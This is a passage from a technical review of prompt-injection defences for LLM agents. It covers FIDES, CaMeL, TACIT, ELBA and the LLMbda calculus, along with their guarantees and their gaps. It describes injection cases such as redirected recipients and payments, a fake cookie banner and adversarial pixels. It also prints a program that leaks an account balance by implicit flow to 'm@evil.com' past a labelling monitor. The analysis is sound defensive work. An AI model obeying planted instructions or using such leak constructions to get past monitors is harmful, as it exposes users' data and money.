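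An attacker who controls the recipient of a private message can have it sent to them. If the attacker controls only the body, they can change what the recipient reads, but the message still goes to the person the user chose. The confidentiality check also still prevents the body from including anything that person may not read.

In the earlier hotel example, FIDES would store the hotel's web page in a variable, so the context would stay trusted and the agent could send Dana the message with the office address. For the calendar entry, the planning model could use a quarantined model to extract the check-in time, then pass on the result by variable name. The decision to create an entry would be trusted but the time would not, so the strict policy would still refuse the call. A policy that accepted untrusted text in calendar entries would allow it. Variables remove the restriction on actions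 that don't depend on the page, but someone still has to decide which arguments may depend on it.

That decision is easy to get wrong. Even a message body can be dangerous if it contains a link, because the web address can carry private data to the attacker's server. In their tests, Costa and colleagues therefore block messages that contain untrusted links.

Payments are riskier. *SPA* gives the example of an invoice with an attacker's bank account on it. The agent can follow exactly the steps the user wanted and still pay the attacker. The account number determines where the money goes, just as a recipient determines where a message goes, so it should come from a trusted source. But for payments, the policy in the FIDES tests checks only the choice of tool, not the labels of its arguments, so it would allow the payment if the account number came from a variable.

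### Three email tasks

Costa and colleagues compare designs by applying a simple rule to three tasks. Under the rule, a tool call is safe if the planning model generated it from trusted inputs alone. When the model passes a variable by name, the variable's contents don't count as one of the model's inputs.

The simplest task is to send the top three emails in a mailbox to someone as a chat message. In the basic loop, the model reads the emails and then writes the message, so it generates the second call from untrusted text and breaks the rule. With variables, the model requests the emails, gets back a variable name, and requests a message with that name as the body. It needs no information from the emails to do this.

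The next task is to summarise the three emails and send the summary. Variables alone are not enough, because a model has to read the emails to summarise them. The planning model would break the rule if it read them itself, but it can ask a quarantined model for the summary and send the result by its variable name.

The last task is to check whether any of the three emails contains a meeting request and, if so, to create a calendar event. Now the planning model needs information from the emails to decide whether to create the event. A quarantined model can find the answer, but the planning model can't act on it while it stays hidden in a variable.

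Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if one sequence of tool calls, with one final response, completes it whatever the stored data says. Let D be the set of possible starting states of the mailbox and other stored data. Let S(d) be the set of action sequences that complete the task from state d, leaving out queries to the model. The task is data-independent if

⋂ S(d) ≠ ∅, taken over all d in D,

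and data-dependent otherwise. For the email examples to fit this definition, a call that passes a variable has to count as the same call whatever the variable contains. Forwarding and summarising are then data-independent. The meeting task is data-dependent because the correct sequence creates an event if there is a request and does not create one if there isn't.

The table shows which designs can complete each task within the rule, assuming that the planning model never opens a variable containing free text.

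| Task | Basic loop | Variables only | Variables and a quarantined model | Variables and a quarantined model with constrained answers |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Forward three emails | breaks the rule | yes | yes | yes |
| Summarise them and send the summary | breaks the rule | no | yes | yes |
| Create an event if an email asks for a meeting | breaks the rule | no | no | only if the policy accepts a yes or no from untrusted data |

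How much each addition helps depends on the task. Costa and colleagues sorted the AgentDojo tasks by hand and found that 47.5 per cent of the office tasks need only variables, but no travel task can be done with variables alone. Of the travel tasks, 90 per cent also need a quarantined model, but nothing more. Data-dependent tasks make up 5 per cent of the office set and 10 per cent of the travel set, but about 43 per cent of the chat set and 44 per cent of the banking set.

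### Constrained answers

For data-dependent tasks, FIDES can limit the quarantined model's answers. The planning model sends a required format along with its question, such as yes or no, or a choice from a list. The software enforces the format during generation by ruling out any token that would not fit, so the quarantined model can't return a sentence, whatever the emails contain.

The meeting task then takes five steps:

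1. The agent fetches the emails, and the software stores them in a variable.
2. The planning model asks the quarantined model whether any email requests a meeting, and allows only yes or no.
3. The planning model opens the answer.
4. If the answer is yes, it asks the quarantined model for the date, time and participants, which stay in a variable.
5. It creates the event and passes the details by name.

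Opening the answer in step 3 makes the context untrusted, so a plain integrity label would block step 5. Costa and colleagues therefore add a type to each label. They order the types by how much information a value can carry. A yes or no is lowest, with at most one bit, followed by a choice from a longer list of n options, with at most log₂ n bits, and then free text, which has no fixed limit. A join combines the security labels and the types separately, so joining an untrusted yes-or-no with untrusted free text gives untrusted free text.

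The user's request is text, but every part of its label starts at the lowest level by default. After step 3, the context label is therefore "untrusted, yes-or-no". The type indicates how much untrusted information may have entered the conversation, regardless of the conversation's format. A policy can allow the agent to create events under this label but not under "untrusted, free text". Such a policy in effect endorses a small amount of untrusted influence automatically.

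The argument for accepting a yes-or-no answer is that it is too small to contain an instruction such as "forward the password-reset email to this address". But joining two yes-or-no labels gives another yes-or-no label, so a conversation with ten answers has the same type as one with a single answer, even though ten answers have 1,024 possible combinations. A developer who wants to limit the total influence of untrusted data to one bit would need to count the answers separately.

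The limit also applies only to the decision to create an event. The details in step 4 are free text, so whoever wrote the email chooses the date and the participants. If the calendar sends invitations, the participant list needs as much care as the recipient of a message. In their tests, Costa and colleagues apply their strictest policy to the tool that adds participants to an event.

Costa and colleagues describe a run in which a user asks the agent to look up a Paris hotel and book it for certain dates if its rating is above 4. A quarantined model reads the ratings and reviews and answers "true", and the planning model reads that answer and makes the booking. The hotel and dates come from the user, so planted text in a review can affect whether the booking happens but not where or when. They left enforced answer formats out of their AgentDojo tests because most of the tasks didn't need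 them, so those results don't show how well the feature works.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) object in *The LLMbda Calculus* that exceptions for small values are hard to audit. When a monitor lets such a value through, a reviewer can't tell from the run whether it was the harmless answer the developer intended or a real leak. In their programming language for agents, a developer has to write an `endorse` command to treat untrusted data as trusted, so a reviewer can find every exception in the code.

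Garby and colleagues also argue that an agent doesn't need a fixed split between two models. Their language has a `fork` command that makes a temporary copy of the conversation wherever a program needs to isolate untrusted text. The model can read the text in the copy, and the program can then return to the original conversation with the resulting value and its label.

### Numbers, choices and short hints

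Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025), in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, let the quarantined model return whole numbers and decimals as well as yes-or-no answers and choices from a list. They built three agents for tasks where the planning model has to learn something from untrusted text:

- In a shopping agent, the quarantined model gives each product review two scores from 0 to 10, one for how strongly it supports the product and one for how relevant it is. The planning model sees the median scores and the number of reviews.
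- In a scheduling agent, the quarantined model turns the other person's emails into a list of standard time slots. A description of the meeting stays in a variable.
- In a bug-fixing agent, the quarantined model turns a public bug report into a bug category and a list of places in the code, which it gives as file numbers and line numbers. Another agent uses these to write three repair plans without seeing the report. A model that has seen the report then chooses a plan by returning its number.

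The attack success rate fell to zero in all three cases. Jacob and colleagues choose types by whether a value can express an instruction, whereas Costa and colleagues order them by how much information they can carry. The two criteria can give different results, since a long list of numbers could encode a sentence. Jacob and colleagues therefore limit the length of lists.

Processing each piece of untrusted data separately also helps. Willison relates an example from *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents* (2025) in which an agent has to find this month's invoices and send them to the accounting department. The agent makes a separate model call for each file, which returns only whether that file is relevant. A malicious file can affect whether it is included, but it can't change the result for any other file.

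*Twin Agent* (2026) takes a looser approach. One agent explores the untrusted material and sends compact hints to a second agent, which acts on them. A developer can set a budget for the hints to balance usefulness against security. The design did well in tests on coding and office tasks, but it has no formal guarantee, and stronger attacks might defeat it.

### False answers from a quarantined model

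None of these designs ensures that the quarantined model's answers are true. In the summary task, Costa and colleagues note, an instruction in one email could make the quarantined model write an empty summary. The agent would then make the right calls in the right order but send a blank message. Such an instruction could also make the model leave out an important email or invent a deadline. A policy that required a trusted message body would prevent this, but it would also block every accurate summary of untrusted emails.

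One AgentDojo attack is meant to make an AI travel agent tell the user that a certain place is gorgeous and worth visiting. Costa and colleagues don't count this as a real injection, because it changes no tool call and reveals nothing confidential. The text keeps its untrusted label, so an application could mark it as untrusted on the screen, but the user may still book a trip because of it.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) explains the limit by separating control flow from data flow. Control flow is which calls run, in what order and under what conditions. Data flow is the values in the arguments and conditions. The two-model design protects control flow from injected instructions, but attackers can still affect data flow. For example, if a plan branches on a yes-or-no answer, a false answer can select a branch that the plan allows but the user would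 not want.

Policies on arguments help only when the arguments have a clear meaning. A monitor can check the recipient field of a tool that sends email. But an agent that operates a computer through its screen may act by clicking at certain coordinates, and that click could log in, delete data or open a malicious site, depending on what is displayed there.

An answer in a constrained format can still be false. In the meeting task, a false yes creates an unwanted event, and a false no hides a real request. Jacob and colleagues exclude misleading inputs from the attacks they defend against. In their shopping agent, taking the median limits the effect of a single dishonest review, but a seller who posts enough fake reviews can still raise the score without any prompt injection.

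Hiding text can also leave the planning model with too little information. One banking task in AgentDojo requires the agent to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. FIDES showed the model the trusted amounts and dates but hid the descriptions. In some runs, the model classified a large payment as suspicious and changed the password without opening the description. This was a guess, but AgentDojo counted the task as completed, and no policy had been broken.

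### Tasks that require following a document

Some users ask for what an integrity policy forbids. A user might ask an agent to pay a bill according to the instructions in a file, or to complete today's tasks from a to-do list. If the file or list is untrusted, the agent can't do the task unless untrusted text determines its action.

Many of the banking tasks in AgentDojo are like this. Costa and colleagues examined the tasks that FIDES failed and found that most of the failures were intended. Reading the file made the context untrusted, and the policy then blocked the agent from scheduling the payment or updating the user's details.

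Constrained answers help if the developer can list the possible actions in advance. Costa and colleagues suggest letting a quarantined model choose among scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply and forwarding an email. But whoever writes the untrusted text can then trigger any action on the list, so the list should contain only actions the user would let a stranger trigger. A to-do list can contain any request, so no short list of actions would cover it. Foerster and colleagues describe tasks like this, where the untrusted data itself specifies the sequence of actions, as a fundamental limitation of both FIDES and CaMeL.

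A more capable model would not remove the conflict, just as better screening would not have helped with the chat tasks in the RTBAS tests. A genuine invoice that says "pay this account" gets the same label as a planted one with the same sentence. To tell them apart, someone has to either establish who could have written the file or endorse the payment.

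## Does it help to have the model write a program that is then checked?

FIDES checks each tool call, but the plan behind the calls stays inside the planning model, which chooses one call at a time. A model can instead write the whole plan as a program before anything runs. Software can then read the plan's steps, conditions and dependencies, so methods made for ordinary programs apply again. Only the program's calls to a language model remain opaque, and the output of each such call must still be treated as depending on all of that call's inputs.

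### From a request to a checked program

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) introduced CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind. A planning model reads the user's request, but no emails, files or web pages, and writes a program in a restricted version of Python. An interpreter runs the program, records where each value came from, and checks each tool call against a policy.

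Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, describes a gap in his two-model pattern that this approach closes. Suppose a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and says that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. A sentence planted in the notes cannot add a step to the plan, but it could make the quarantined model that looks up Bob's address return the attacker's address instead. The assistant would then send the document to the attacker while still following its original plan.

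In CaMeL, the planning model might turn the request into a program like this simplified one:

```
notes    = find_meeting_notes()
address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's address?", notes)
title    = ask_quarantined("Which document does Bob want?", notes)
document = fetch_document(title)
send_email(to=address, subject="As promised", attachment=document)
```

As the interpreter works through these lines, it tags each value with its sources and its permitted readers. By the last line, it has recorded the following sources:

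| Value | Where it came from |
|---|---|
| `address` | the meeting notes |
| `document` | the stored document, and the notes, because `title` determined which document to fetch |
| subject line | the user's request |

Suppose the policy for sending email requires a trusted recipient who may read everything in the message. Other people can edit the notes, so the tag on `address` doesn't mark it as trusted. For a similar request, Willison describes a policy that allows the email if the user already trusts the address, and otherwise has the system ask the user, as it would for the attacker's address. A planted sentence could also change `title`, and the program would then fetch a different document. The check on readers would stop that document only if Bob isn't allowed to read it. If he is allowed, the program would send him the wrong document without breaking any policy.

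The planning model wrote the subject line from the request alone, so the subject line counts as trusted even though the program read the notes before sending the email. In the basic agent loop, the subject line would have had the same label as the notes.

A program can also contain the condition for an action. In the earlier task of creating an event if an email requests a meeting, FIDES had to show the planning model a yes or no, which made the model's context untrusted. With CaMeL, the planning model can write the `if` statement in advance, and the interpreter evaluates it without showing the model the answer. According to *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026), this guarantees for a single agent that untrusted data cannot add a new branch to the plan, though it may affect which of the planned branches runs.

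The interpreter can also track the conditions that determine whether an action runs. Garby and colleagues give the example of a program that emails an outsider if an account balance is above a threshold. The email contains no figure from the account, but CaMeL blocks it because the decision to send it depends on the balance. They also found programs that leak a secret despite this tracking.

Willison points out that this design also helps privacy, because the company that hosts the planning model sees the user's request but none of their emails or files. Extracting an address is easier than planning, so the quarantined model can be small enough to run on the user's own computer.

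### Rejecting a program before it runs

CaMeL finds a forbidden flow only when the program reaches it. In many programming languages, a type checker can find some errors before the program runs. A type describes the kind of value an expression produces, such as a number or text, and the checker rejects a program that uses a value in a way its type does not allow. In some languages, the type of a piece of code also describes the effects it can have, such as writing to a file.

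*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) uses the types of the Scala 3 language to restrict agents. In its system, TACIT, an agent acts by submitting short Scala programs. A capability here is an object, such as an open file or a network connection, that code must hold to have an effect. (CaMeL uses the same word for its tags.) A function's type lists every capability the function can use.

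When a program reads a confidential file, it gets the contents inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent's code cannot take the contents out. It can only give the wrapper a function to apply to them, and the result comes back wrapped. The wrapper accepts only functions that use no capabilities. A function can count the words in a confidential document because counting affects nothing outside the function. If the function also writes the text to a log file, its type includes the log file, and the compiler rejects the program before any of it runs.

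This rule also prevents implicit flows, such as booking a meeting room only when a confidential memo announces a merger. The agent's code can work out whether the memo announces a merger, but the answer is also wrapped, and an `if` statement cannot test a wrapped value. The code cannot make the booking inside the wrapper either, because booking requires a capability. As a result, the agent can't make a booking that depends on the memo even when its user wants one, unless someone with permission unwraps the answer.

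Odersky and colleagues assume that the model writing the programs may be hostile. When its code prints a wrapped value, the model receives only asterisks, while the user sees the real text on her screen. To summarise a confidential contract, the code passes the wrapped text to a separate model, which returns a wrapped summary. The developer must trust that second model not to keep the text or pass it on.

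Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of passwords, access keys and confidential documents. They gave each of two models 120 combinations of an ordinary task with a planted instruction, and 11 requests in which the user tried to obtain the secrets. With the secrets wrapped, none appeared in either agent's output. Without the wrapper, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in 2 of the 131 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11. The researchers designed this test around the property that the types enforce, so the absence of leaks mainly confirms that the software works as intended. The more informative result is that the agents still completed 99 and 90 per cent of the ordinary tasks with the secrets wrapped.

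The type check restricts what an agent's code can do, regardless of why the agent wrote it. Odersky and colleagues argue that a harmful injection must either send private data to the wrong place or use a capability the agent was never given. Their argument overlooks harm done with a capability the agent does have. If an agent can pay suppliers and reads an unwrapped email from a stranger, a program that pays the stranger could pass the type check. Wrapping the email would prevent this by hiding it from the agent, as variables do in FIDES.

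### Sub-agents that read untrusted data and keep some tools

A CaMeL plan cannot change in response to unexpected data, and the quarantined model that reads the data has no tools. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) relaxes both restrictions. Its system, ELBA, uses Haskell, a language in which a program's type shows all its effects. A developer calls the function `agent` with a prompt, a set of permitted operations and the type of result she expects. A model then writes a Haskell program, which runs only if it has that type.

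If the expected type is a whole number, for example, the program can calculate but cannot have any effect. If a user asks a calculator agent to delete every file on the server and then compute a factorial, the model may write that program, but the type checker will reject it because deleting files is an effect.

Types can also record where data came from. Zhou and colleagues built an agent that compiles reference lists. The only operation that writes to the list requires entries of a type called `Trusted`, which the agent can get only by fetching them from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. Across 100 tasks, none of its 925 citations had a wrong author, year or identifier. An ordinary agent that had a web search tool and wrote the citations itself got 19 of 1,002 wrong.

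For information flow, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library. LIO keeps a current label for the running program, much like the context label in the basic loop. The type checker ensures that the agent's program acts only through LIO, and LIO checks the label before each action while the program runs.

Unlike the basic loop, LIO lets a program do part of its work in a separate block with its own label. Suppose an agent has to write a colleague a message based on a web page:

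1. The agent's program starts a sub-agent in a separate block and gives it the task.
2. The sub-agent reads the page, which makes the block's label untrusted. The main program's label does not change.
3. The sub-agent can still call tools, and LIO checks each call against the block's label.
4. The sub-agent returns the message as a labelled value that the main program cannot read without raising its own label.
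5. The main program passes the value unread to the messaging tool, which checks the recipient and the message's label before sending it.

In step 3, Zhou and colleagues' policies allow a sub-agent that has read an untrusted page to open a fixed web address it found there. The sub-agent may not put private data in the address or make any web request after reading sensitive data. These policies limit what untrusted text can trigger, as constrained answers do in FIDES, but the sub-agent can choose the order and arguments of its actions after reading the text.

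Any program the sub-agent writes must pass the same type check, so the sub-agent cannot give itself more permissions than the agent that started it. Zhou and colleagues prove that if Haskell guarantees a property for every well-typed program, the property also holds when agents write parts of the program. The proof holds whatever the model writes, because the type checker rejects code that is not well-typed.

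Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA on the chat tasks in AgentDojo. The four models they used, including Opus 4.8 and GPT 5.4, resisted every standard attack even without policies, so those attacks could not show whether the policies worked. The researchers therefore simulated a successful injection by deleting the sub-agent's real task and leaving only the text that contained the attacker's instruction. Without policies, 16 to 42 per cent of these attacks succeeded, depending on the model, while with policies none of the 735 attacks on each model did. The policies also reduced the share of tasks completed from 67 to 76 per cent down to 40 to 48 per cent.

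### What each system checks and what it trusts

| | CaMeL | TACIT | ELBA with LIO |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before the program runs | No check of data flow | The capabilities each function uses, and whether confidential data stays wrapped | Whether the program acts only through permitted operations |
| While it runs | The sources and readers of the data in each tool call | File paths, commands and network addresses | The label of everything the program or sub-agent has read |
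| Can the planning model react to tool results? | No, it plans from the request | Yes, except to wrapped contents | Yes, by starting sub-agents that read them |
| What the developer must trust | The interpreter, the tags and the policies | The Scala compiler, the capability library, the software that runs the code, and the model that reads confidential text | The Haskell compiler, LIO, and the tools with their labels |

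A check before execution covers every input and every branch. If the check fails, the program has not done anything yet, so there is no half-finished task to clean up. But the checker must reject a program even if its only forbidden branch would never have run.

Some checks have to wait until the program runs. For example, a program may build a file path from data it has just read, so a type checker cannot determine in advance whether the path leads outside the permitted folder. TACIT and ELBA check paths during execution. ELBA also follows links between folders, so a permitted path cannot lead to a forbidden file.

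Each system can also fail if a component it trusts has a fault. ELBA has an advantage because researchers have studied LIO and proved properties of it for years. CaMeL depends on a custom interpreter, and Garby and colleagues note that it has no comparable proof. Odersky and colleagues report computer-checked proofs for the core of Scala's capability types, but not yet for the restricted version of Scala that agents must use. TACIT's static checks also cover only the Scala program. If an agent may run an outside command, TACIT can check which command it is but not what the command does with its data.

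### What planning in advance costs

A planning model that cannot see the data has to guess its form. The program for Bob's document is written for notes that contain one address and name one document. If the notes contain two addresses, or Bob appears as "Robert", the program may fail or use the wrong value. CaMeL lets the planning model try again after a failure, but a failure may depend on secret data, so Garby and colleagues warn that repeated attempts can leak that data.

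With ELBA, the model has to write a new program only after a type error, which the checker finds before the program calls any tool. This happened about 0.13 times per run on AgentDojo and took up 3.4 per cent of the running time. In 7 of 2,688 runs, the model failed to write an acceptable program within the permitted number of attempts. In a test of TACIT with simulated airline and retail customers, 0.3 to 8 per cent of programs needed correcting, usually only once.

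ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL on AgentDojo, mainly because its agents call a model again whenever they need to decide what to do with new data. But it completed about twice as many chat tasks with policies enforced. Each system had its own policies, and there were only 21 tasks, so the difference may not be due to the design alone.

Developers also have to describe their tools in the new language. TACIT has about 1,000 lines of code that every application can share, and the descriptions for the airline and retail tests took a few hundred lines each. CaMeL restricts the programs themselves. According to Odersky and colleagues, the planning model cannot define its own functions or write functions that call themselves.

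A plan written in advance works least well for open-ended tasks. When a programmer looks for a bug, the result of one test determines what to try next, so nobody could list all the branches beforehand. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents* accepts this kind of limit, and Willison reports that its patterns deliberately stop agents from solving arbitrary tasks.

The difficulty comes from planning without the data, not from writing code. TACIT's agents can read ordinary results as they go, and on a benchmark of real software bugs, MiniMax M2.5 fixed 41.7 per cent with TACIT and 43.3 per cent with ordinary tool calls. In the airline and retail test, all three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher when they wrote Scala. Odersky and colleagues think the compiler's error messages and the structured results helped.

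### Agents that operate a screen

An agent that uses a computer through its screen normally takes in the screen's contents before every click. Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL to such agents by having a planning model write a program without access to the screen, with a branch for each situation it can predict. As the program runs, a quarantined vision model describes the screen, and another call compares the description with an expected condition, such as "a cookie banner is visible". The interpreter then takes the matching branch. If that branch requires a click, the vision model supplies the coordinates.

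These programs averaged 213 lines, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, 5 calls and 4 branches for CaMeL's programs on AgentDojo. About half the steps were fallbacks that did not run.

Foerster and colleagues tested the design on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in desktop applications such as a web browser and a spreadsheet. They report that it retains up to 57 per cent of a frontier model's performance, based on 109 tasks that an undefended agent running on Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed. The protected agent completed 62 of these tasks in at least one of five attempts, but only 31, or 28 per cent, with one attempt. To benefit from five attempts, a user would need a way to tell which one had worked, and on a real computer the failed attempts could leave unwanted changes behind.

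The comparison also depends on a weakened baseline. To save time and money, Foerster and colleagues limited the undefended agent to 15 steps per task, and it scored 37.7 per cent on the full benchmark, compared with the published 58.1 per cent.

They also report a 19 per cent improvement for a small open model, UI-TARS. That result compares the best of three protected attempts with what appears to be one unprotected attempt. With one attempt each, the protected agent completed 51 of the 339 tasks that software could score, and the unprotected agent completed 60.

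The planning model mattered more than the model that looked at the screen. On a shared set of 60 tasks, three very different screen models led to success rates between 65 and 68 per cent over five attempts. Foerster and colleagues also compared nine planning models, all from 2025, on 17 tasks, and GPT-5 completed the most, with 12. They expect better planners to improve the results without any change to the design.

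Another version, built on FIDES, completed 67 per cent of the 60 tasks over five attempts. It used 29.6 times as many tokens as an undefended agent, because it sent the planning model the whole history at every step. The CaMeL version used 1.88 times as many as the undefended agent.

In both versions, a false answer can still make the program take the wrong branch. Many plans begin by looking for a cookie banner and dismissing it. Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie banner inside an advertisement, and the agent clicked it and went to the attacker's website. The click was part of the plan, so the interpreter allowed it.

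One defence compared the screenshot with the web page's underlying code. It stopped simple image advertisements but not interactive ones that concealed what they were. The other defence asked a second model to confirm each location before the agent clicked. An advertisement with specially altered pixels got past that check, even at a setting so strict that it often blocked harmless clicks.

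## What do the proofs guarantee, and what can still leak?

A security proof covers one stated property under stated assumptions. The strongest property researchers ask of an agent is noninterference, which means that changing the secret inputs changes nothing an outsider can observe. FIDES is designed for a weaker property, CaMeL has no comparable proof, and the LLMbda calculus comes close to full noninterference. The three systems differ mainly in how they treat information that an agent reveals without copying any of it.

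### What a monitor can tell from one run

Fred Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) identifies which policies a monitor can enforce if it can only watch a program run and stop it. Whether a run complies with such a policy must depend on that run alone. Every violation must also be detectable after a finite number of steps, and nothing later may undo it, since otherwise the monitor would have no definite point at which to stop the program. Policies that meet these conditions are called safety properties. "Never send an email after opening the payroll file" is a safety property, but "Answer every customer eventually" is not, because stopping a program can't make it answer anyone.

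Noninterference compares runs, so it is not a safety property. The earlier agent, for example, books a meeting room after reading a confidential memo. The booking reveals a merger if the agent books only when the memo announces one, but reveals nothing if the agent would have booked the room anyway. The monitor records the same read and the same booking in both cases, and this record doesn't show what the agent would have done with a different memo.

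A monitor can still achieve noninterference by enforcing a stricter rule that implies it, such as "book nothing after opening a confidential memo". That rule also stops an agent that would have booked the room regardless of what the memo said. It works only if outsiders can't tell that the monitor refused a booking.

### An assignment that never runs

A monitor can handle conditions by labeling whatever the program does inside them. When a program reaches `if balance > threshold`, the next steps depend on the balance, so the monitor adds the balance's label to every variable that those steps change. CaMeL tracks conditions this way.

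J. S. Fenton described a way around such tracking in 1974, and Denning rewrote it as ordinary program code. Garby and colleagues adapted it to CaMeL, with a program of this form:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The table follows the two possible runs.

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance not above it |
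|---|---|---|
| `tmp = True`, `rich = True` | both public | both public |
| `if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False` | runs; `tmp` is now False and secret | skipped; `tmp` stays True and public |
| `if tmp: rich = False` | skipped; `rich` stays True and public | runs; `rich` is now False and public |
| `if rich: send_email(...)` | sends the email | does nothing |

The program sends the email exactly when the balance is above the threshold, yet the monitor treats `rich` as public in both runs. In the first run, a secret value makes the program skip `rich = False`. The monitor adds labels only when assignments run, so `rich` stays public even though its value reveals that the balance is above the threshold. The leak depends on the second variable, because if the program set `rich` to True directly inside the secret condition, `rich` would become secret and the monitor would refuse the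 email.

When the whole program is written before it runs, software can prevent this leak by reading both branches in advance and labelling every variable that either could change. This doesn't work when a model chooses one call at a time, because the calls it didn't make were never written.

Austin and Flanagan (2009) proposed stopping the program before it changes a public variable inside a secret condition. Here, the program would stop at `tmp = False`, before sending anything. This prevents the email from revealing that the balance is above the threshold, but anyone who can see that the program stopped still learns it.

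The LLMbda calculus applies the same rule to conversations. In one of its examples, a program tells the model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model to set x to true, and finally it asks for x. The conversation corresponds to `rich`, because when the secret is false, the program skips the middle message and the conversation would keep its public label. The interpreter therefore stops any run that would add a message to a public conversation because of a secret.

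### What FIDES guarantees

Costa and colleagues chose a property called explicit secrecy, which rules out unwanted explicit flows but does not restrict implicit flows. Their definition uses a datastore d, which holds everything the tools can read and write, such as mailboxes, files and calendars. Each item in d is either public or secret, and d₁ =ʟ d₂ means that the datastores d₁ and d₂ have the same public items.

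Take any run, or part of a run, that starts from d₁. Let g be the combined effect of its tool calls on the datastore. This is a function: it applies the same calls, with the same arguments and in the same order, to whatever datastore it receives. The agent satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every d₁ and every such g,

d₁ =ʟ d₂ implies g(d₁) =ʟ g(d₂), for all d₂.

The definition requires that replaying the same calls on a datastore with different secrets leave the same public items. A call that copies the salary file into a public folder fails this test, because different salaries would end up in the folder. The agent that books a room only if the memo mentions a merger passes, because the replay repeats the original run's calls whatever the memo says. Since the definition holds the calls fixed, it doesn't cover cases where different secrets would have led the agent to make different calls.

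Read literally, the formula covers even less than that. Text that a tool has returned to the conversation is part of the planner's state, not the datastore, and g keeps every argument from the original run. If an agent reads a salary and types it into a public post, the replay posts the same figure whatever the salary file contains, so the formula is satisfied. FIDES is stricter than the formula here and would refuse the post, because the argument has the context label, which includes the salary's label.

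Costa and colleagues write that their labelled loop can enforce explicit secrecy. They define the property and prove a lemma about how runs transform the datastore, but they give no separate theorem that the loop satisfies the definition. Garby and colleagues refer to a noninterference theorem for FIDES in their introduction, but later describe the guarantee as explicit secrecy, as the FIDES paper does.

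Costa and colleagues judged full noninterference too restrictive because it would essentially forbid any call that may write public data after any call that may read secret data. Suppose FIDES has stored two public web pages in variables, and the planning model then opens a confidential memo. The agent can also post pages to the company's website. The confidentiality policy checks the label of the data in the post, and both pages are public, so the monitor would allow either one. The agent's choice between them may reveal something about the memo. Noninterference would prevent that leak by forbidding both posts, including the one the user wanted. TaintDroid and several web browsers make the same compromise as FIDES.

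### Noninterference when the model chooses at random

Garby and colleagues prove a form of noninterference that covers implicit flows. They first had to write a definition that compares probabilities instead of single results, because a model generates its words randomly.

For each starting point, a program in the calculus gives every final outcome a probability. These probabilities may add up to less than 1 because some runs never finish, and a run that the interpreter stops for breaking a rule is counted as never finishing. The definition groups outcomes that an observer at a given level m cannot tell apart.

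Let P and Q be the probabilities for two starting points that look the same to the observer and differ only in their secrets. The strictest definition would require P = Q. The one that Garby and colleagues use requires P and Q to be compatible, which means that there is some R with

P(x) ≤ R(x) and Q(x) ≤ R(x) for every outcome x, and Σ R(x) ≤ 1.

Intuitively, P and Q are compatible if the only thing separating them is runs that didn't finish. Suppose an agent publishes announcement A or announcement B, and its probabilities depend on a secret number:

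| Secret number | Publishes A | Publishes B | Never finishes |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.5 | 0.5 | 0 |
| 2 | 0.5 | 0.3 | 0.2 |
| 3 | 0.7 | 0.3 | 0 |

The rows for 1 and 2 are compatible, because R can be 0.5 for each announcement. The rows for 1 and 3 are incompatible, because R would have to be at least 0.7 for A and at least 0.5 for B, which adds up to at least 1.2. A program that produced all three rows would therefore violate the property.

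Garby and colleagues prove that every program in the calculus satisfies this condition at every level m, a property they call termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. The theorem covers agents that ask a model for code and then run it, because the interpreter runs that code under the label of the conversation it came from. The proof assumes nothing about what an attacker can get the model to write.

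Compatible results can still leak a little. Announcement B makes up 50 per cent of the finished runs with secret number 1, but 37.5 per cent with secret number 2. Someone who sees many finished runs could notice the difference. Garby and colleagues prove that half the sum of the gaps between P and Q is at most the average of their probabilities of not finishing. In this example, both figures are 0.1. If a program always finishes, that average is zero, so P must equal Q.

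The proof constructs R using a hypothetical second interpreter that skips every part of the program whose label is above the observer's level and puts an empty value in its place. This interpreter never uses the secrets, so it gives the same probabilities for both starting points. It also finishes at least as often as the real one, because a program cannot get stuck in a step that is skipped. Its probabilities are therefore at least as high as those in both P and Q, as the definition requires of R.

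### Endorsement without releasing secrets

LLMbda's `endorse` command, which marks untrusted data as trusted, deliberately breaks noninterference for integrity. Garby and colleagues prove that `endorse` leaves confidentiality intact. When a program endorses a value, the result takes its integrity from the label that the program names but keeps the value's confidentiality. Endorsing untrusted secret text produces trusted text that is still secret, so a program cannot release a secret by endorsing it.

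The theorem guarantees noninterference for an observer who ignores integrity labels, whatever untrusted inputs an attacker supplies and however often the program endorses them. The mathematics is symmetrical, so a similar command for declassification would weaken confidentiality but not integrity.

Endorsement can still be unsafe, because the basic calculus doesn't stop a planning model from endorsing too freely. One optional restriction prevents endorsed code from generating code with further endorsements. Another limits endorsement to a small set of values, much like the constrained answers in FIDES.

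Garby and colleagues wrote the proofs in Lean, a language whose software checks every step of a proof. The interpreter that runs the agents is also written in Lean, and a theorem shows that it produces each result with the probability given by the mathematical definition. This removes a common weakness, in which the program a developer runs differs from the one the proof describes.

The proofs do not cover the code that contacts the model over the network. They assume that each answer comes from a fixed probability distribution for that conversation, so they would not apply to a hosted model that carried information between conversations by another route. The tools are simulated inside the program, and Garby and colleagues list their treatment of external tools and data as a limitation.

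### The gaps in CaMeL

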